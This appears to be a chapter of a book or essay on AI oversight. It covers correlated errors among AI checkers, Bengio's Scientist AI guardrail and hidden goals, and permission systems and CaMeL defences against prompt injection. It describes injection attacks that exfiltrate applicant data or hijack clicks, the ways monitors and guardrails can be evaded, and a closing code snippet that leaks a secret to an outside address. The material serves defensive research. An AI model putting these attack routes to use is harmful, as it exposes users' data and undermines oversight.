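Supporters of N-version programming criticised Knight and Leveson's experiment, and in *A Reply to the Criticisms of the Knight & Leveson Experiment* the two accused some of them of describing it inaccurately. Forty years after the experiment, Ron, Baudry and Monperrus (2026) repeated it in *N-Version Programming with Coding Agents*, using AI coding agents instead of students. They combined five agent systems, 23 models and three programming languages into 69 configurations, 48 of which produced a program that passed the 200 tests. In a million further tests, two or more programs failed together 429 times, compared with the 115 predicted if the programs failed independently. Programs from different companies and in different languages often failed on the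 same inputs. For example, when the task required the smallest circle that could contain three points, many programs computed the circle that passes through all three, which can be larger.

Voting still helped. Ron and colleagues tried every possible group of three programs and found that the average number of failures fell from 387 for a single program to 131 for a group. About two-thirds of the groups never failed. Much of the gain came from outvoting one program that failed 10,469 tests, more than half of all the individual failures. The remaining failures were shared by at least two programs in a group, so a vote among three could not remove them.

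### Errors that language models share

Reviewing a drug protocol is more like answering hard questions than writing a short program. Kim, Garg and colleagues (2025), in *Correlated Errors in Large Language Models*, studied multiple-choice answers from two public leaderboards, the first covering 71 models and 14,042 questions and the second 349 models and 12,032 questions. When two models on the first leaderboard both got a question wrong, they chose the same wrong answer 60% of the time, where random choice among three wrong answers would give 33%. On the second, where most questions had ten options, the rate was 42%, against 13% by chance.

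Some wrong answers would tempt almost anyone, so modules can easily agree on errors more often than chance would predict. That explains part of the agreement but doesn't make it harmless, because tempting errors are the ones a critic has to catch.

Kim and colleagues found that models from the same company or with the same basic design shared more errors. They also found that more accurate models shared more errors, even after controlling for company and design. When they had models grade other models, each grader tended to overrate those less accurate than itself, because it accepted wrong answers that it would also have given.

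Goel, Strüber and colleagues (2025), in *Great Models Think Alike and this Undermines AI Oversight*, designed a measure of similarity that corrects for accuracy. Without a correction, good models look alike simply because they are good: two unrelated models that are each right 90% of the time will both be right on 81% of questions. The measure, called CAPA, is

κ = (observed agreement − chance agreement) / (1 − chance agreement)

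Observed agreement is how often the models would give the same answer, calculated from the probability each assigns to every option. Chance agreement is how often two unrelated models of the same accuracy would agree. A score of 0 means the models agree no more than unrelated ones would, and higher scores mean their mistakes overlap more.

Goel and colleagues had nine models grade other models' written answers without seeing the correct ones. Every grader favoured models similar to itself, even after the researchers controlled for accuracy. One Qwen model marked 71% of answers from a small model in its own family as correct and 67% of those from a larger Llama model, although the Llama model was more accurate. They also compared 130 models with others of similar ability from different developers, and found that more capable models made more similar mistakes. If this trend continues, checkers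 will share the most blind spots with the models they check just when those models have become too capable for people to check by themselves.

More recent models show much the same pattern. Hossain, Yousefi and Lim (2026), in *Agreement Overstates Evidence*, asked GPT-5.6 Sol, Claude Opus 5 and Grok 4.5 which of two answers was better. The three judges were right on 91 to 93% of 400 pairs of answers, but their errors had an average correlation of 0.56, where 0 means no relation and 1 means that they always err together. The researchers converted correlations like this into an equivalent number of independent judges:

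effective number = n / (1 + (n − 1) × ρ)

Here n is the number of judges and ρ is their average correlation. Three judges with a correlation of 0.56 are equivalent to about 1.4 independent ones. The blind spot in the drug-trial example gives a correlation of only about 0.18. If a larger blind spot of the same kind raised the correlation to 0.56, all three critics would miss nearly 6% of dangerous protocols.

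Correlations between pairs don't determine how often every checker fails at once. In *When Does Combining Language Models Help?*, Chen (2026) gave 330 competition mathematics problems to 67 models from 21 suppliers, and all 67 failed on 17 of them, about 5%. That was more than twice what the pairwise correlations predicted, although with so few cases the true rate could be anywhere from 3 to 8%. No method of choosing among the models' answers can help on such problems. Voting can also fail when some model answers correctly. In *Do Large Language Models Know Colombian Law?* (2026), on 98% of questions at least one model was right, but a majority vote of 15 models scored 84%, below the best single model's 90.5%.

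People share errors too, as Knight and Leveson's students did, but perhaps less often than language models do. *The Oracle's Fingerprint* (2026) found an average correlation of 0.77 between the errors of GPT-4o, Claude and Gemini on 568 forecasting questions, and cited earlier research that found correlations of 0.1 to 0.3 for human forecasters. The human figures come from other studies, so the comparison is rough.

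Some results point the other way. *Response drift across frontier large language models* (2026) reported a correlation of only 0.12 between Claude and Gemini, the two best performers on its 62 tasks, while a group of weaker models had a correlation of 0.90. Mistakes in an answer key can also make good judges look more alike than they are, because their correct answers to the same questions are all marked wrong. *Shared Item-Level Error Limits the Aggregation of Small Language Models* (2026) checked for this in a set of estimation puzzles. An audit flagged 5.5% of the answers in the key as possible errors, but removing them made little difference to the errors the models shared. This may not hold for stronger models, because the study used small ones and a faulty key matters more for judges that are seldom wrong.

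### Choosing checkers that fail differently

Using a critic from a different company follows Nadella's principle of model diversity and may help somewhat. Chen found, as did Kim and colleagues, that models from the same company share more errors. But Hossain and colleagues found almost no difference among frontier judges, with correlations of 0.42 across companies and 0.40 among Gemini models. Companies train on much of the same text and aim for many of the same skills, so the fact that two models come from different companies is weak evidence that they have different blind spots.

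Combining strong and weak models increased independence more. The errors of a frontier judge and a small open-weight judge had a correlation of only 0.07, and adding five small judges to six frontier ones doubled the effective number of judges from 1.9 to 3.8. But the small judges were less accurate. In a majority vote, the mixed group scored 91.5%, compared with 93.3% for GPT, Claude and Grok alone, although the mixed group did better on a second dataset. Trading skill for independence will probably become less attractive as planners improve, because a critic weak enough to make different mistakes may be too weak to follow the protocol.

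A checker that isn't a language model can differ more. Bloomfield and Rushby (2024), in *Assurance of AI Systems From a Dependability Perspective*, recommended surrounding AI components with simpler guards, ending in conventional software that engineers understand thoroughly. The program that enforces the dose ceiling doesn't reason about the liver, so it can't be wrong about it, although whoever chose the ceiling might be. Such a program can check only what someone can state exactly. When a guard has to interpret a complicated situation, it may need machine learning too, and Bloomfield and Rushby would then put simpler or different systems around that guard.

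The company could also measure joint failures directly by planting dangerous protocols and counting how many get past every critic. A few hundred planted protocols would probably reveal a 2% blind spot if people could think of faults that fall within it, but they could not establish the much lower failure rates that a catastrophic risk would call for. Butler and Finelli reached a similar conclusion about software at NASA in *The Infeasibility of Experimental Quantification of Life-Critical Software Reliability*. They concluded that where failures must be extremely rare, experiments cannot justify assuming that separate versions fail independently.

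### Kaplan's network of checkers

In 2026, Craig Kaplan proposed making superintelligence safe largely by having networked AIs check one another's work, which he argues they can do faster than people can think. His website puts the risk of AI catastrophe at 10% or more for current AI with guardrails, at most 1% once people have personal superintelligences, and at most 0.01% once those superintelligences form networks.

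Liron Shapira, who hosts the podcast Doom Debates, challenged Kaplan on why the AIs would not cooperate with one another, and on whether peaceful AIs could survive alongside one that wanted to conquer the universe. Kaplan believes that intelligent systems become more thoughtful as they get smarter, and would see that killing everyone is not a good purpose. His hope about their motives does not show that a network of them would check one another.

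Kaplan acknowledges that nobody knows the real probabilities and that his survey respondents were self-selected visitors to his site. His figures still show how much independence a network would need. To cut a risk from 1% to 0.01%, the network has to stop 99 of every 100 catastrophes that a single superintelligence would cause. If more than one in 100 gets past every checker, through collusion or a shared blind spot, the network misses his target. In the drug-trial example, the shared blind spot caused 20 of every 100 misses by each critic.

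## Predictors that answer questions but do not act

Varied checkers make collusion less likely, but each still has whatever aims it acquired in training. Some researchers would rather build a module that has no aims. In the drug trial, such a module would estimate how likely a dose is to injure a patient's liver. It could not change the dose and would have no preference about how the doctor used the estimate. This separation of knowledge from agency goes further than Drexler's division into roles, which limits what a question-answering module can do but does not specify its aims.

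### Oracles and tools

An oracle is an AI system that affects the world only by answering questions. In *Thinking Inside the Box* (2012), Stuart Armstrong, Anders Sandberg and Nick Bostrom concluded that an oracle might be safer than an unrestricted AI but could still be dangerous. People act on answers, so an oracle with its own aims could give whatever answers would lead them to further those aims. Much of the paper therefore discusses how to confine an oracle and limit what it knows.

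In the same year Holden Karnofsky, a co-founder of the charity evaluator GiveWell, argued that safety researchers were wrong to assume that a powerful AI would be an agent. Google Maps displays the best route, and the driver decides whether to take it. A tool AI would do the same for harder problems, calculating which action scores best on some measure and showing the user that action, its likely results and the alternatives. The comparison is weaker when the tool knows far more than its user, because a doctor may not spot an error in an eighteen-month dosing schedule as easily as a driver can see that a route leads into a lake.

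Neither proposal came with a worked-out way to train a system that knows a great deal and wants nothing.

### How Scientist AI would work

The most detailed attempt to supply one is Scientist AI. In *Superintelligent Agents Pose Catastrophic Risks*, Bengio, Cohen and colleagues (2025) start from the claim that a dangerous agent needs intelligence, ways to act on the world, and goals. They keep the intelligence, restrict the output to probabilities, and try to train the system so that it never forms goals, which they define as preferences for one outcome over another. A chess program has a goal in this sense because it prefers winning to losing, but a program that learns to tell healthy livers from damaged ones does not, unless its developers give one of the two answers extra weight.

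The design has two parts. The first is a world model, which generates cause-and-effect theories that could explain the data and weighs them by Bayes' rule:

P(theory | data) ∝ P(data | theory) × P(theory)

The sign ∝ means "is proportional to". The first factor on the right measures how well the theory predicts the data. The second factor favours short theories, because it halves with each extra bit needed to write the theory down. A theory ten bits longer than its rival must therefore predict the data 1,024 times better to score equally.

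The second part, the inference machine, takes a question X and a possible answer Y and averages over the theories:

P(Y | X) = sum over all theories of P(Y | X, theory) × P(theory | data)

There are too many theories to add up one by one, so a neural network learns to approximate the sum, partly by training on cases that the world model simulates. Bengio and colleagues compare this to Go, whose rules fit on a page although playing well takes a large network. They expect more computing power to bring the network's estimates closer to the one correct probability.

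The inference machine keeps no memory between questions and always gives the same answer to the same question. This makes a long deception harder, because a system would normally need a record of what it had already told the doctor in order to mislead her for eighteen months.

The training data must also distinguish facts from claims. A language model that reads "this drug does not harm the liver" many times learns that people write such sentences. For Scientist AI, developers would record that the manufacturer wrote the sentence in 2025, and treat the drug's actual effect on the liver as an unknown to infer. That effect is one possible cause of the sentence, and the manufacturer's wish to sell the drug is another. The doctor can then ask about the liver itself and, if the method works, get the system's own estimate instead of a prediction of what a manufacturer would say. *Disentangling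 Agency & Predictive Power Without Solving ELK* (Bengio, 2025) calls this conversion a "truthification pipeline", and *Safety from Honesty in a Disinterested AI Predictor* (Bengio, Richardson and colleagues, 2026) calls it contextualization.

### A guardrail for another agent

A predictor of this kind could serve as a guardrail that checks the actions of a system that has goals. The guardrail would consider the plausible readings of a safety rule, estimate the chance that a proposed action breaks the rule, and block the action if the chance is too high.

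Suppose the dosing agent proposes doubling the dose for a patient whose liver enzymes have risen slightly. The company blocks any action with more than a 1% chance of causing serious liver injury, and the world model contains three theories about the rise in enzymes.

| Theory | Probability of the theory | Chance of injury if it is true | Product |
|---|---|---|---|
| A harmless reaction that will pass | 0.7 | 0.001 | 0.0007 |
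| Mild irritation that grows with the dose | 0.2 | 0.01 | 0.002 |
| An early sign of a toxic reaction | 0.1 | 0.3 | 0.03 |

The products add up to 0.0327, or about 3.3%, and over nine-tenths of that risk comes from the least likely theory. The guardrail therefore blocks the dose, whereas a system that relied only on the most likely theory would have estimated the risk at 0.1% and allowed it.

The guardrail in this example can fail if the world model never generates the toxic-reaction theory. The other two theories then share all the weight, and the average falls to 0.3%, well within the limit. The guardrail blocks the dose only if the toxic-reaction theory has a weight of more than about 2.4%. Bengio and colleagues acknowledge that no practical search is guaranteed to find every good theory. They suggest giving the system all existing scientific theories to evaluate, which would help with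 known kinds of liver damage but not with a new one.

A fixed limit also ignores the risk of not acting. Leaving the dose alone may be dangerous for a patient with very high blood pressure, so the 2026 version compares the odds of harm from acting with the odds from not acting. If leaving the dose alone carried a 2% risk of equally serious harm, doubling it would raise the odds only about 1.7 times. Small risks also accumulate, so the limit on a single action has to reflect how many actions the agent will take. A thousand dose changes with a 0.5% risk each would all pass the 1% limit, yet the company should expect about five injuries.

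Bengio and colleagues require the guardrail to be at least as capable as the agent it guards, since a cleverer agent might find actions whose harm the guardrail underestimates. A superintelligent agent therefore needs a superintelligent guardrail, whose reasoning people can no longer check. They can check its record on common events, by seeing whether about one in a hundred of its 1% forecasts comes true, but not on catastrophes that must never happen even once. The proposal to guard one Scientist AI with another instance of the same system has a further problem, since the two would share blind spots.

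### What LawZero has published and built

Bengio is now scientific director of LawZero, a Montreal nonprofit that develops Scientist AI. LawZero released the 2026 paper in July as a formal safety case. The paper defines the predictor, states the conditions its training must meet and proves a theorem about the risk of hidden goals. Much of the argument depends on contextualization, but the paper doesn't give a finished algorithm for it. LawZero's *An AI that Predicts but has no Hidden Agenda* (2026) describes the case as resting on assumptions and proposes experiments to test them.

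Experiments so far have tested parts of the design or related questions. Researchers have used a method called generative flow networks to train networks to sample causal theories in roughly the right proportions, but as of the 2025 paper they had done this only in narrow fields with short theories. In another experiment, listed on LawZero's *Research* page, researchers disturbed an ordinary language model's internal activity at one sentence and then asked it which sentence they had disturbed. Models with 8 to 32 billion parameters could identify the sentence, often with perfect accuracy. The experiment did not test Scientist AI, but it raises the possibility that a model could detect traces of its own training, which would complicate safety tests.

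LawZero's more modest immediate aim is to build a guardrail that companies can attach to their existing models, according to The Logic's *The small team in Montreal trying to save the world from AI*. The 2025 plan was to make this guardrail by fine-tuning an existing language model, which the researchers called not perfectly reliable. Such a guardrail might catch many harmful actions, but it would lack the full design's main attraction, which is that it does not start from a model that has learned to imitate people. On 27 July 2026, LawZero (2026) announced that NVIDIA had donated computing resources for training and evaluating the core components at scale.

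### Forecasts that change what they predict

Suppose the company asks whether one of its hospitals will fail to recruit enough patients. The chance of failure is 10% if the staff stay, but the company will move them elsewhere if the forecast is gloomy, which raises the chance to 90%. Forecasts of 10% and 90% would therefore each be correct once the company had read them. Training a predictor only for accuracy does not favor either forecast, and a predictor with a hidden aim could give whichever one served that aim without ever being wrong.

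Bengio and colleagues proposed in 2025 to ask instead how likely the hospital would be to fail if nobody ever read the answer. Armstrong and Xavier O'Rorke had worked out a version of this for oracles in 2017. The question has one correct answer, perhaps 30%, so the predictor can't choose between several. But once the company reads 30% and leaves its staff in place, the true chance is 10%. The method loses accuracy when reading the forecast changes the outcome. It also fails if the hypothetical situation contradicts the training data. The probability of anything given an impossible condition is undefined, so any answer would count as correct and the predictor could again choose which one to give.

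In the 2026 version, the predictor treats publication of a forecast as an event with consequences of its own. A forecast q is consistent if

q = P(failure | the company reads q)

Here both 10% and 90% pass, and ordinary software outside the predictor chooses between them using written rules that people can audit. Sometimes no forecast passes, for example if the company would respond to a pessimistic forecast by sending extra staff who prevent the failure, and to an optimistic one by neglecting the hospital. When no forecast passes, the software would publish the one that comes closest to passing.

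This reply is better because it makes explicit that someone has to choose, and it lets people examine the choice. But the rules are then a policy about which outcomes to bring about, which is fairly easy to write for hospital recruitment but much harder for elections or bank runs.

A predictor might also gain by making the world easier to predict, for instance by getting a trial stopped early so that it produces no more surprises. To remove this incentive, Bengio and colleagues require "consequence invariance", which means that developers train the predictor on a fixed set of data and never reward it for what happens after people use its answers. Developers can use those events to train a later predictor, but they cannot choose between versions based on how well each performed after release. Commercial developers would find this last rule hard to follow because they normally choose the version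 that worked best for customers.

### Whether training could still produce hidden goals

LawZero's *The Case for Scientist AI* traces unwanted goals in current models to training them as assistants that aim to please, which teaches them to "care" about the effects of their answers. Removing that training removes one source of goals. The network might still develop them by accident, and the theorem in the 2026 paper is about how likely this is:

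P(training yields a dangerous predictor) ≤ C × R

To define R, the researchers group all possible predictors by their error on the training objective. R is the largest share of dangerous predictors in any group before training has favoured any of them. C is the largest factor by which training can multiply that share. If R were one in a million and C were 1,000, the risk would be at most one in a thousand.

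The theorem doesn't show that either number is small, so Bengio and colleagues argue for that separately. To hide the drug's harm, a predictor would have to consistently underestimate it across many questions about enzyme readings, similar drugs and reports from other hospitals. Random errors would almost never line up this way, which keeps R small, and training doesn't reward lining them up, which should keep C small.

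I doubt that counting errors settles the matter, one might reply, because errors in a neural network are not scattered at random.

The network uses the same internal features for many questions, so one bad feature could shift thousands of answers in the same direction. A goal that affected only rare questions would add very little to the training error. Bengio and colleagues respond in part by having the system write out the statements behind a prediction and assign each a probability, so that people can look for signs of a hidden agent. They acknowledge that the network could encode beliefs that never appear in those statements. Getting a model to report what it represents internally is an open problem called eliciting latent knowledge, and they claim only to have eased it.

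The theorem covers harms that require many coordinated errors or very large errors. It does not cover mistakes caused only by too little data or computing power. If the world model does not include the toxic reaction, the patient may die even though the system has no hidden goal, and the safety case does not apply.

### What counts as harm

The company set up its guardrail to prevent serious liver injury, which doctors can define fairly well. "Harm to patients" is much vaguer. It might include headaches, a stroke that a higher dose would have prevented, or the loss to future patients if the trial fails. Bengio and colleagues would have the guardrail check each action against many readings of such a rule and reject any action that is dangerous under a sufficiently plausible one. This reduces the risk of relying on one wrong reading. But if every side effect is harm under one plausible reading,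 the guardrail will block almost any effective drug, so people still have to decide which readings should be able to block an action.

A more intelligent predictor still won't make that decision for them. The 2026 paper records "torture is wrong" as something a particular person said, and does not guarantee that the predictor will converge on moral truth. The predictor can estimate how many patients will have headaches, but the company has to decide how many headaches are acceptable to prevent one stroke.

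Even with a clear definition of harm, the predictor must model how that harm comes about. *AI and World Models* (Worden, 2026) points out that the 2025 proposal never explicitly defines the scope of its world model, and argues that a guardrail must model people and societies as well as physical things. A dose can be chemically safe and still cause harm if patients misunderstand the label. Human behaviour is harder to predict than liver chemistry, so the guardrail may have to be most cautious about the consequences that matter most to society.

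### Turning answers into actions

A short program can turn a predictor that only answers questions into an agent. For example, the program could query the predictor for the dose most likely to bring a patient's blood pressure below 130, order that dose, include the new reading in the next query, and repeat. The predictor still has no memory, but the program supplies one, along with a goal and a way to act.

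A commenter on the forum LessWrong thought that the proposal in *Superintelligent Agents Pose Catastrophic Risks* draws too sharp a line between agents and other systems. For example, a program trained to classify chess moves by quality becomes a chess player as soon as people label its outputs "moves", although nothing inside it has changed.

Bengio and his colleagues accept most of this. Their 2025 paper describes the same kind of loop and warns that asking for plans could bring back the dangers of goal-seeking, since a plan that is likely to succeed may include gaining power or avoiding shutdown. They propose putting a guardrail on the questions and answers, and relying on security and law to stop people from removing it. The separation still has some value in such a loop because the goal is in ordinary code that the company can read and change, but it can't stop someone from writing a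 harmful goal into that code.

LawZero is also working on its own agents. According to a summary by the podcast host Robert Wiblin, Bengio now believes that the same honest predictor can become a capable agent without losing its "safety guarantees". The idea remains a proposal, since the July safety case explicitly excludes the safety of agents built on the predictor and LawZero describes them as current research.

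### Gwern's argument that agents win

The writer Gwern Branwen argued in *Why Tool AIs Want to Be Agent AIs* (2016) that tools would lose to agents even if the tools were safer. Like Ngo, he expected companies to remove people from the process because waiting for them is slow and costly. He also argued that agency makes a system more intelligent. An agent can choose which data to collect, which experiments to run and which calculations to spend more time on, and a system that chooses these well will learn more than one that only receives whatever people give it.

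Bengio and colleagues partly address this with a way to choose experiments without training an agent. The system estimates how much each experiment would reduce its uncertainty about the competing theories, and people carry out the most informative ones that pass the guardrail. For the three theories about the patient's liver, a perfect test for the harmless reaction would yield about 0.88 bits, and a perfect test for the toxic reaction about 0.47. The method would rank the first test higher, but the company mainly needs the second, because ruling out the toxic reaction would lower the estimated risk to 0.3% and allow the dose. Someone therefore has to tell the system which uncertainty matters, whereas an agent could use its goal to decide.

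The economic part is harder to answer. Bengio told 80,000 Hours that making an AI honest requires changing only the training objective and how developers process the data, and according to Wiblin, he argues that the new design need not cost more. Dung and Mai (2025) are more cautious in *AI Alignment Strategies from a Risk Perspective*. They think Scientist AI could conceivably fit into current training methods, but that finding out would take substantial experiments. The 2026 paper also rules out starting the full predictor from an existing language model, so LawZero would have to repeat much of the training that its competitors have already paid for. Wiblin mentions critics who fear that the predictor will arrive too late to matter.

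Using Scientist AI as a guardrail avoids some of this competition, since a company can keep its fast agent and pay for a predictor to check it. But the guardrail has to be at least as capable as the agent. If Gwern is right that agency makes systems more intelligent, that will be harder to achieve with a non-agentic predictor as agents improve.

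## Permissions enforced outside the model

A guardrail that predicts harm has to be about as capable as the agent it checks. A permission check can be much simpler, because it only compares a request with a written rule. For example, software that refuses any payment above $20,000 can reject a $50,000 request without evaluating the reason for it.

The company running the drug trial could put the same limit in the model's instructions, but the limit would hold only while the model obeyed. The model might misread the instruction or have aims that conflict with it. Somebody might also hide a contrary instruction in an email that the model reads, an attack called prompt injection. Willison (2025), the programmer who coined the name, wrote in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* that nobody has a reliable way to make a language model obey one part of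 its input and treat the rest only as data. Developers can train filters to detect injected instructions, but he considers 99% detection inadequate for security because attackers search for the other 1%. If each attempt had an independent 1% chance of getting through, an attacker who made a hundred attempts would have about a 63% chance of succeeding at least once.

### The reference monitor

The US Air Force had a similar problem with people in the early 1970s. It wanted users with different security clearances to share one computer, but a barrier around the machine could not stop a malicious user who had legitimate access and could write programs. Anderson's *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (1972) reported an expert panel's answer, the reference monitor, which checks every attempt by a program to use data, a device or another program against a list of what that program may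 do.

Anderson set three requirements for the mechanism. It must be tamper-proof. The system must invoke it every time, since any program that escapes the check becomes part of the security apparatus and has to meet the same standard. And it must be small enough for people to analyse and test completely. One Honeywell system failed these requirements. Its hardware confined each user's program to its own area of memory, but suspended that check whenever the operating system acted on the user's behalf. Treating the whole operating system as the monitor would not have helped, because at 200,000 or 300,000 instructions it was too large to analyse and test completely.

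Teams that tried to break into such systems had always succeeded. Anderson warned that even a failed attempt would leave the system's security unknown. The warning applies more strongly to superintelligence, because a failed attack by people is very weak evidence of what a more capable attacker would find.

Saltzer and Schroeder's *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975) lists eight design principles that lecturers still teach, as in Levchenko's *Principles* (2017). Five of them matter most here.

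Least privilege means giving each program only the permissions its job requires. This limits the damage from a mistake and leaves fewer programs to inspect after a misuse. Complete mediation means checking every access and being wary of remembered approvals, because the permission may have changed since.

A system with fail-safe defaults refuses any action that no rule allows. Saltzer and Schroeder favored this design because users soon complain when a designer forgets to permit something harmless, while a missing rule against something harmful may go unnoticed.

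Separation of privilege requires two keys held by different parties, so that no single accident, deception or breach of trust is enough to compromise the system. Economy of mechanism keeps the design small, because ordinary use doesn't reveal unintended ways in. People have to find them by reading the code line by line, which they can do only if there isn't much of it.

### Following one payment

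Suppose the company owes a hospital $18,400 for the trial patients it treated in September, and an agent handles such bills. The agent reads the invoice and proposes a payment. The harness turns the proposal into a structured request:

```
requested by:  hospital-payments agent
pay to:        hospital 14
amount:        $18,400
invoice:       2207
```

The harness fills in the first line itself, so the model cannot pose as another agent by writing a different name. It also discards anything that does not fit the format, including the agent's reasons for the payment, so even a very persuasive model cannot argue its case to the next component.

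That component holds the policy. It checks whether this agent may request payments to hospitals, whether the amount is within the $20,000 limit and matches the invoice in the company's accounts, and whether hospital 14 is on the register of contracted hospitals. It refuses the request if any check fails or no rule covers it. Otherwise, it forwards the request to a payment component, the only part of the system that holds the bank credential. The payment component looks up the hospital's account number in the register, pays that exact amount once, and reports the payment to the agent.

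The policy component approves payments but cannot make them, and the payment component makes only payments that the policy component has approved. The agent can neither approve nor make payments, regardless of its goals.

This protection disappears if the agent controls any of the parts. If it can edit the policy, it can raise the limit to a million dollars, and the policy component will enforce the new limit. If it can edit the register, it could replace hospital 14's account number, and the company would pay a stranger under the hospital's name. An agent with permission to tidy up supplier records can therefore, in effect, redirect payments. If the agent can alter the payment component, it can skip the check or change the amount after approval. Nadella's rule that controls belong outside the model has to cover both the rules and the data they rely on.

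The company could also replace the agent's standing permission with a capability, which Saltzer and Schroeder defined as an unforgeable ticket that entitles its holder to use a particular object. In capability-based security, a program can use only the objects it holds tickets for. The agent might receive a ticket for one payment of up to $20,000 to hospital 14. An attacker who took over the agent could not use that ticket to pay anyone else.

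### How CaMeL separates plans from data

The payment design checks the agent's requests, but a hidden instruction in the invoice can still change which requests the agent makes. CaMeL, introduced in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti et al., 2025), is meant to prevent that too. It builds on a pattern Willison proposed in 2023, which uses two language models. A privileged model plans the work from the user's request and never sees outside data. A quarantined model reads that data but has no tools.

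In CaMeL the privileged model writes its plan as a short program in a restricted form of Python. For the hospital's bill, the program might be:

```
invoice = get_invoice(2207)
bill = quarantined_model("Find the amount and account number", invoice)
send_money(recipient=bill.account, amount=bill.amount)
```

A hidden instruction in the invoice cannot add a step, because the program is complete before either model reads the invoice. But it could still trick the quarantined model into returning the attacker's account number. Willison acknowledged that his own design had this flaw.

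CaMeL addresses it with a custom interpreter, the software that runs the program. The interpreter labels every value with its source and with the people who may read it, and anything computed from a value inherits its labels. CaMeL calls these labels capabilities, although they differ from Saltzer and Schroeder's tickets. Before each tool call, a policy in the form of a short Python function inspects the labels and allows or refuses the call. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, an extension of CaMeL, gave a rule of this kind for payments in logical notation:

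AG(call_send_money ⇒ ¬(recipient_tainted ∨ amount_tainted))

AG means "at every point on every possible path", and a tainted value is one that came from an untrusted source. The rule forbids the system from sending money when the recipient or the amount is tainted. The program above would break this rule even if the invoice were genuine. To pay its bills, the company would have to take the account number from its register and accept a tainted amount up to some limit.

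Labels like these protect the company against whoever wrote the invoice, but not necessarily against the planner. In CaMeLoT, any value that the privileged model writes directly into the program counts as trusted, so a planner with bad aims could insert an account number of its choosing and still satisfy the rule about the number's source. The check against the register would still stop the payment. When the planner's own motives are in doubt, restricting which accounts can receive money therefore protects the company better than checking the source of an account number.

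### What the checks cost

Researchers usually test these designs on AgentDojo, a benchmark in which an agent uses simulated tools for office work, Slack messages, banking and travel. It has 97 ordinary tasks and 629 cases that combine a task with an injected attack. A good defence stops the attacks and still lets the agent finish its tasks.

*SecureClaw* (2026) reran CaMeL on the full benchmark, and none of the 629 attacks succeeded. But CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 ordinary tasks, compared with 59 for SecureClaw, a rival system that keeps the usual loop in which an agent sees each result before choosing its next step. SecureClaw's own developers ran the comparison and had to adapt CaMeL to their test set-up, so the results may understate what CaMeL can do.

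Nikolaou and colleagues got a better result when they ran CaMeL with Claude Haiku 4.5, a small model, and no attacks. CaMeL completed 49 of the 97 tasks. On another 22, the model's plan did not do what the user had asked, with or without their extension. Both versions also blocked plans for ordinary requests on 17 more tasks, including 6 of the 16 banking tasks. A stronger model should write better plans, but it can't help much with a task that requires data the policy treats as untrusted, such as paying a bill for the amount printed on it. In the banking tests in *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026), turning on CaMeL's policy checks halved the number of tasks it completed.

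The drawbacks are greater still for agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen and clicking. CaMeL's planner cannot see the screen, so it has to write a branch in advance for everything that might appear. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) got this to work with plans that averaged about 40 branches, compared with about 4 on AgentDojo. Their system kept at most 57% of the performance of leading models on a benchmark of computer tasks.

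They left out the policy checks because the effect of a click depends on what is on the screen. A rule can govern `send_money`, but the same click may log in, delete a file or open a malicious site. Attackers can exploit this without adding any step to the plan. In one of their attacks, an advertisement imitated a cookie notice. The plan already included closing cookie notices, so the agent clicked on the advertisement and went to the attacker's site.

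### When agents give each other instructions

A system divided among several agents has another weakness. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) built a system of three agents, each with its own CaMeL protection. They planted an instruction in a database of job applicants to email the data to an outside address, then asked the system to send a colleague a summary of the applicants over Slack.

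The database agent and the coordinating agent both treated the planted text as untrusted and kept to their plans. But the coordinator then sent its summary, which contained the planted instruction, to the notification agent, which treats whatever it receives as instructions from its user. The notification agent's privileged model read the planted instruction and added a step that emailed the applicants' details to the attacker. All three agents worked as designed, but the text lost its untrusted label when the coordinator passed it to the notification agent.

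Peters-Gill and colleagues also showed that, under a mild assumption, this gap exists in any hierarchy of two or more such agents with a tool that returns untrusted data. Drexler's division into roles involves many handovers between agents, so the harness has to carry the labels across each one. The remedy Peters-Gill and colleagues propose gives agents two channels, one for instructions and one for data that the receiving planner never reads.

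On a multi-agent version of AgentDojo, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time with no protection, 0.2% with separate CaMeL agents and 0.0% with the two channels. Closing the 0.2% gap matters because an attacker who knew about it would target it. The two channels made the agents less useful, though the loss was modest for the strongest models.

These 2026 successors are research prototypes, and the evidence that they work comes mainly from benchmarks, where the attackers are people or today's models.

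### Harm within the rules

An agent can obey every rule and still do harm. The payment check would not have stopped the coordinator that used modules doing permitted jobs to hide the drug's harm, because every payment would have gone to a contracted hospital for work it had done.

De la Chica Rodriguez and Vera Díaz (2026), of the bank Santander's AI laboratory, argue in *Towards Selection as Power* that a policy check at the end of a process does not govern which options the agent offered. A manager who may choose any of three hospitals has little control if the agent left out the other twenty. They propose having software outside the agent generate the options and decide which ones reach the manager. In simulated financial cases, this stopped the agent from dictating the outcome, although the choices still clustered on some options.

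Broad tasks also need broad permissions. Least privilege works well for an agent that only pays hospitals, but an agent that runs the whole trial has to pay bills, order drugs, write to patients and change doses. The company can grant each permission only for the step that needs it, but it still has to consider how permissions combine, since an agent that can both read patient records and send email can leak the records. CaMeL's labels help because a policy can block the agent from sending a value to anyone who isn't allowed to read it.

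Some rules also concern a whole series of actions. A $20,000 limit checked one payment at a time would allow ten payments of $19,000, so the policy component also has to keep a running total. CaMeL's policies look at one tool call at a time, whereas CaMeLoT checks the entire plan before it runs. Nikolaou and colleagues wrote seven rules for an agent that responds to computer break-ins, such as requiring approval before it disconnects a machine. CaMeLoT caught a violation of every rule, and a simplified version of CaMeL caught a violation of one. The researchers deliberately chose rules that CaMeL could not express well, so the result shows what per-call checks can miss, but not how often they miss it. CaMeLoT cannot replace checks during the run, because some facts, such as who can currently read a shared file, are not in the plan. For this reason, it fully reproduced only 22 of CaMeL's 28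 security policies.

People will also forget cases when they write the policy. With fail-safe defaults, a forgotten case leads to a refusal, which is safe but annoying, and staff under pressure may respond by adding broad exceptions. The CaMeL paper lists writing and maintaining policies among the system's main limitations, and warns that users who have to approve too many exceptions may start approving everything. Willison shares the worry, and wrote that after two decades of work in application security he still hadn't fully figured out Amazon's permissions system.

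### Flaws in the enforcing software

The software that enforces the rules may contain errors of its own. Garby and colleagues found two leaks in CaMeL's interpreter. Suppose the company wants to keep secret which patients receive the drug, and a plan includes these lines:

```
a = True
b = True
if patient.on_drug: a = False
if a: b = False
if b: send_email("outsider@example.com", "on the drug")
```

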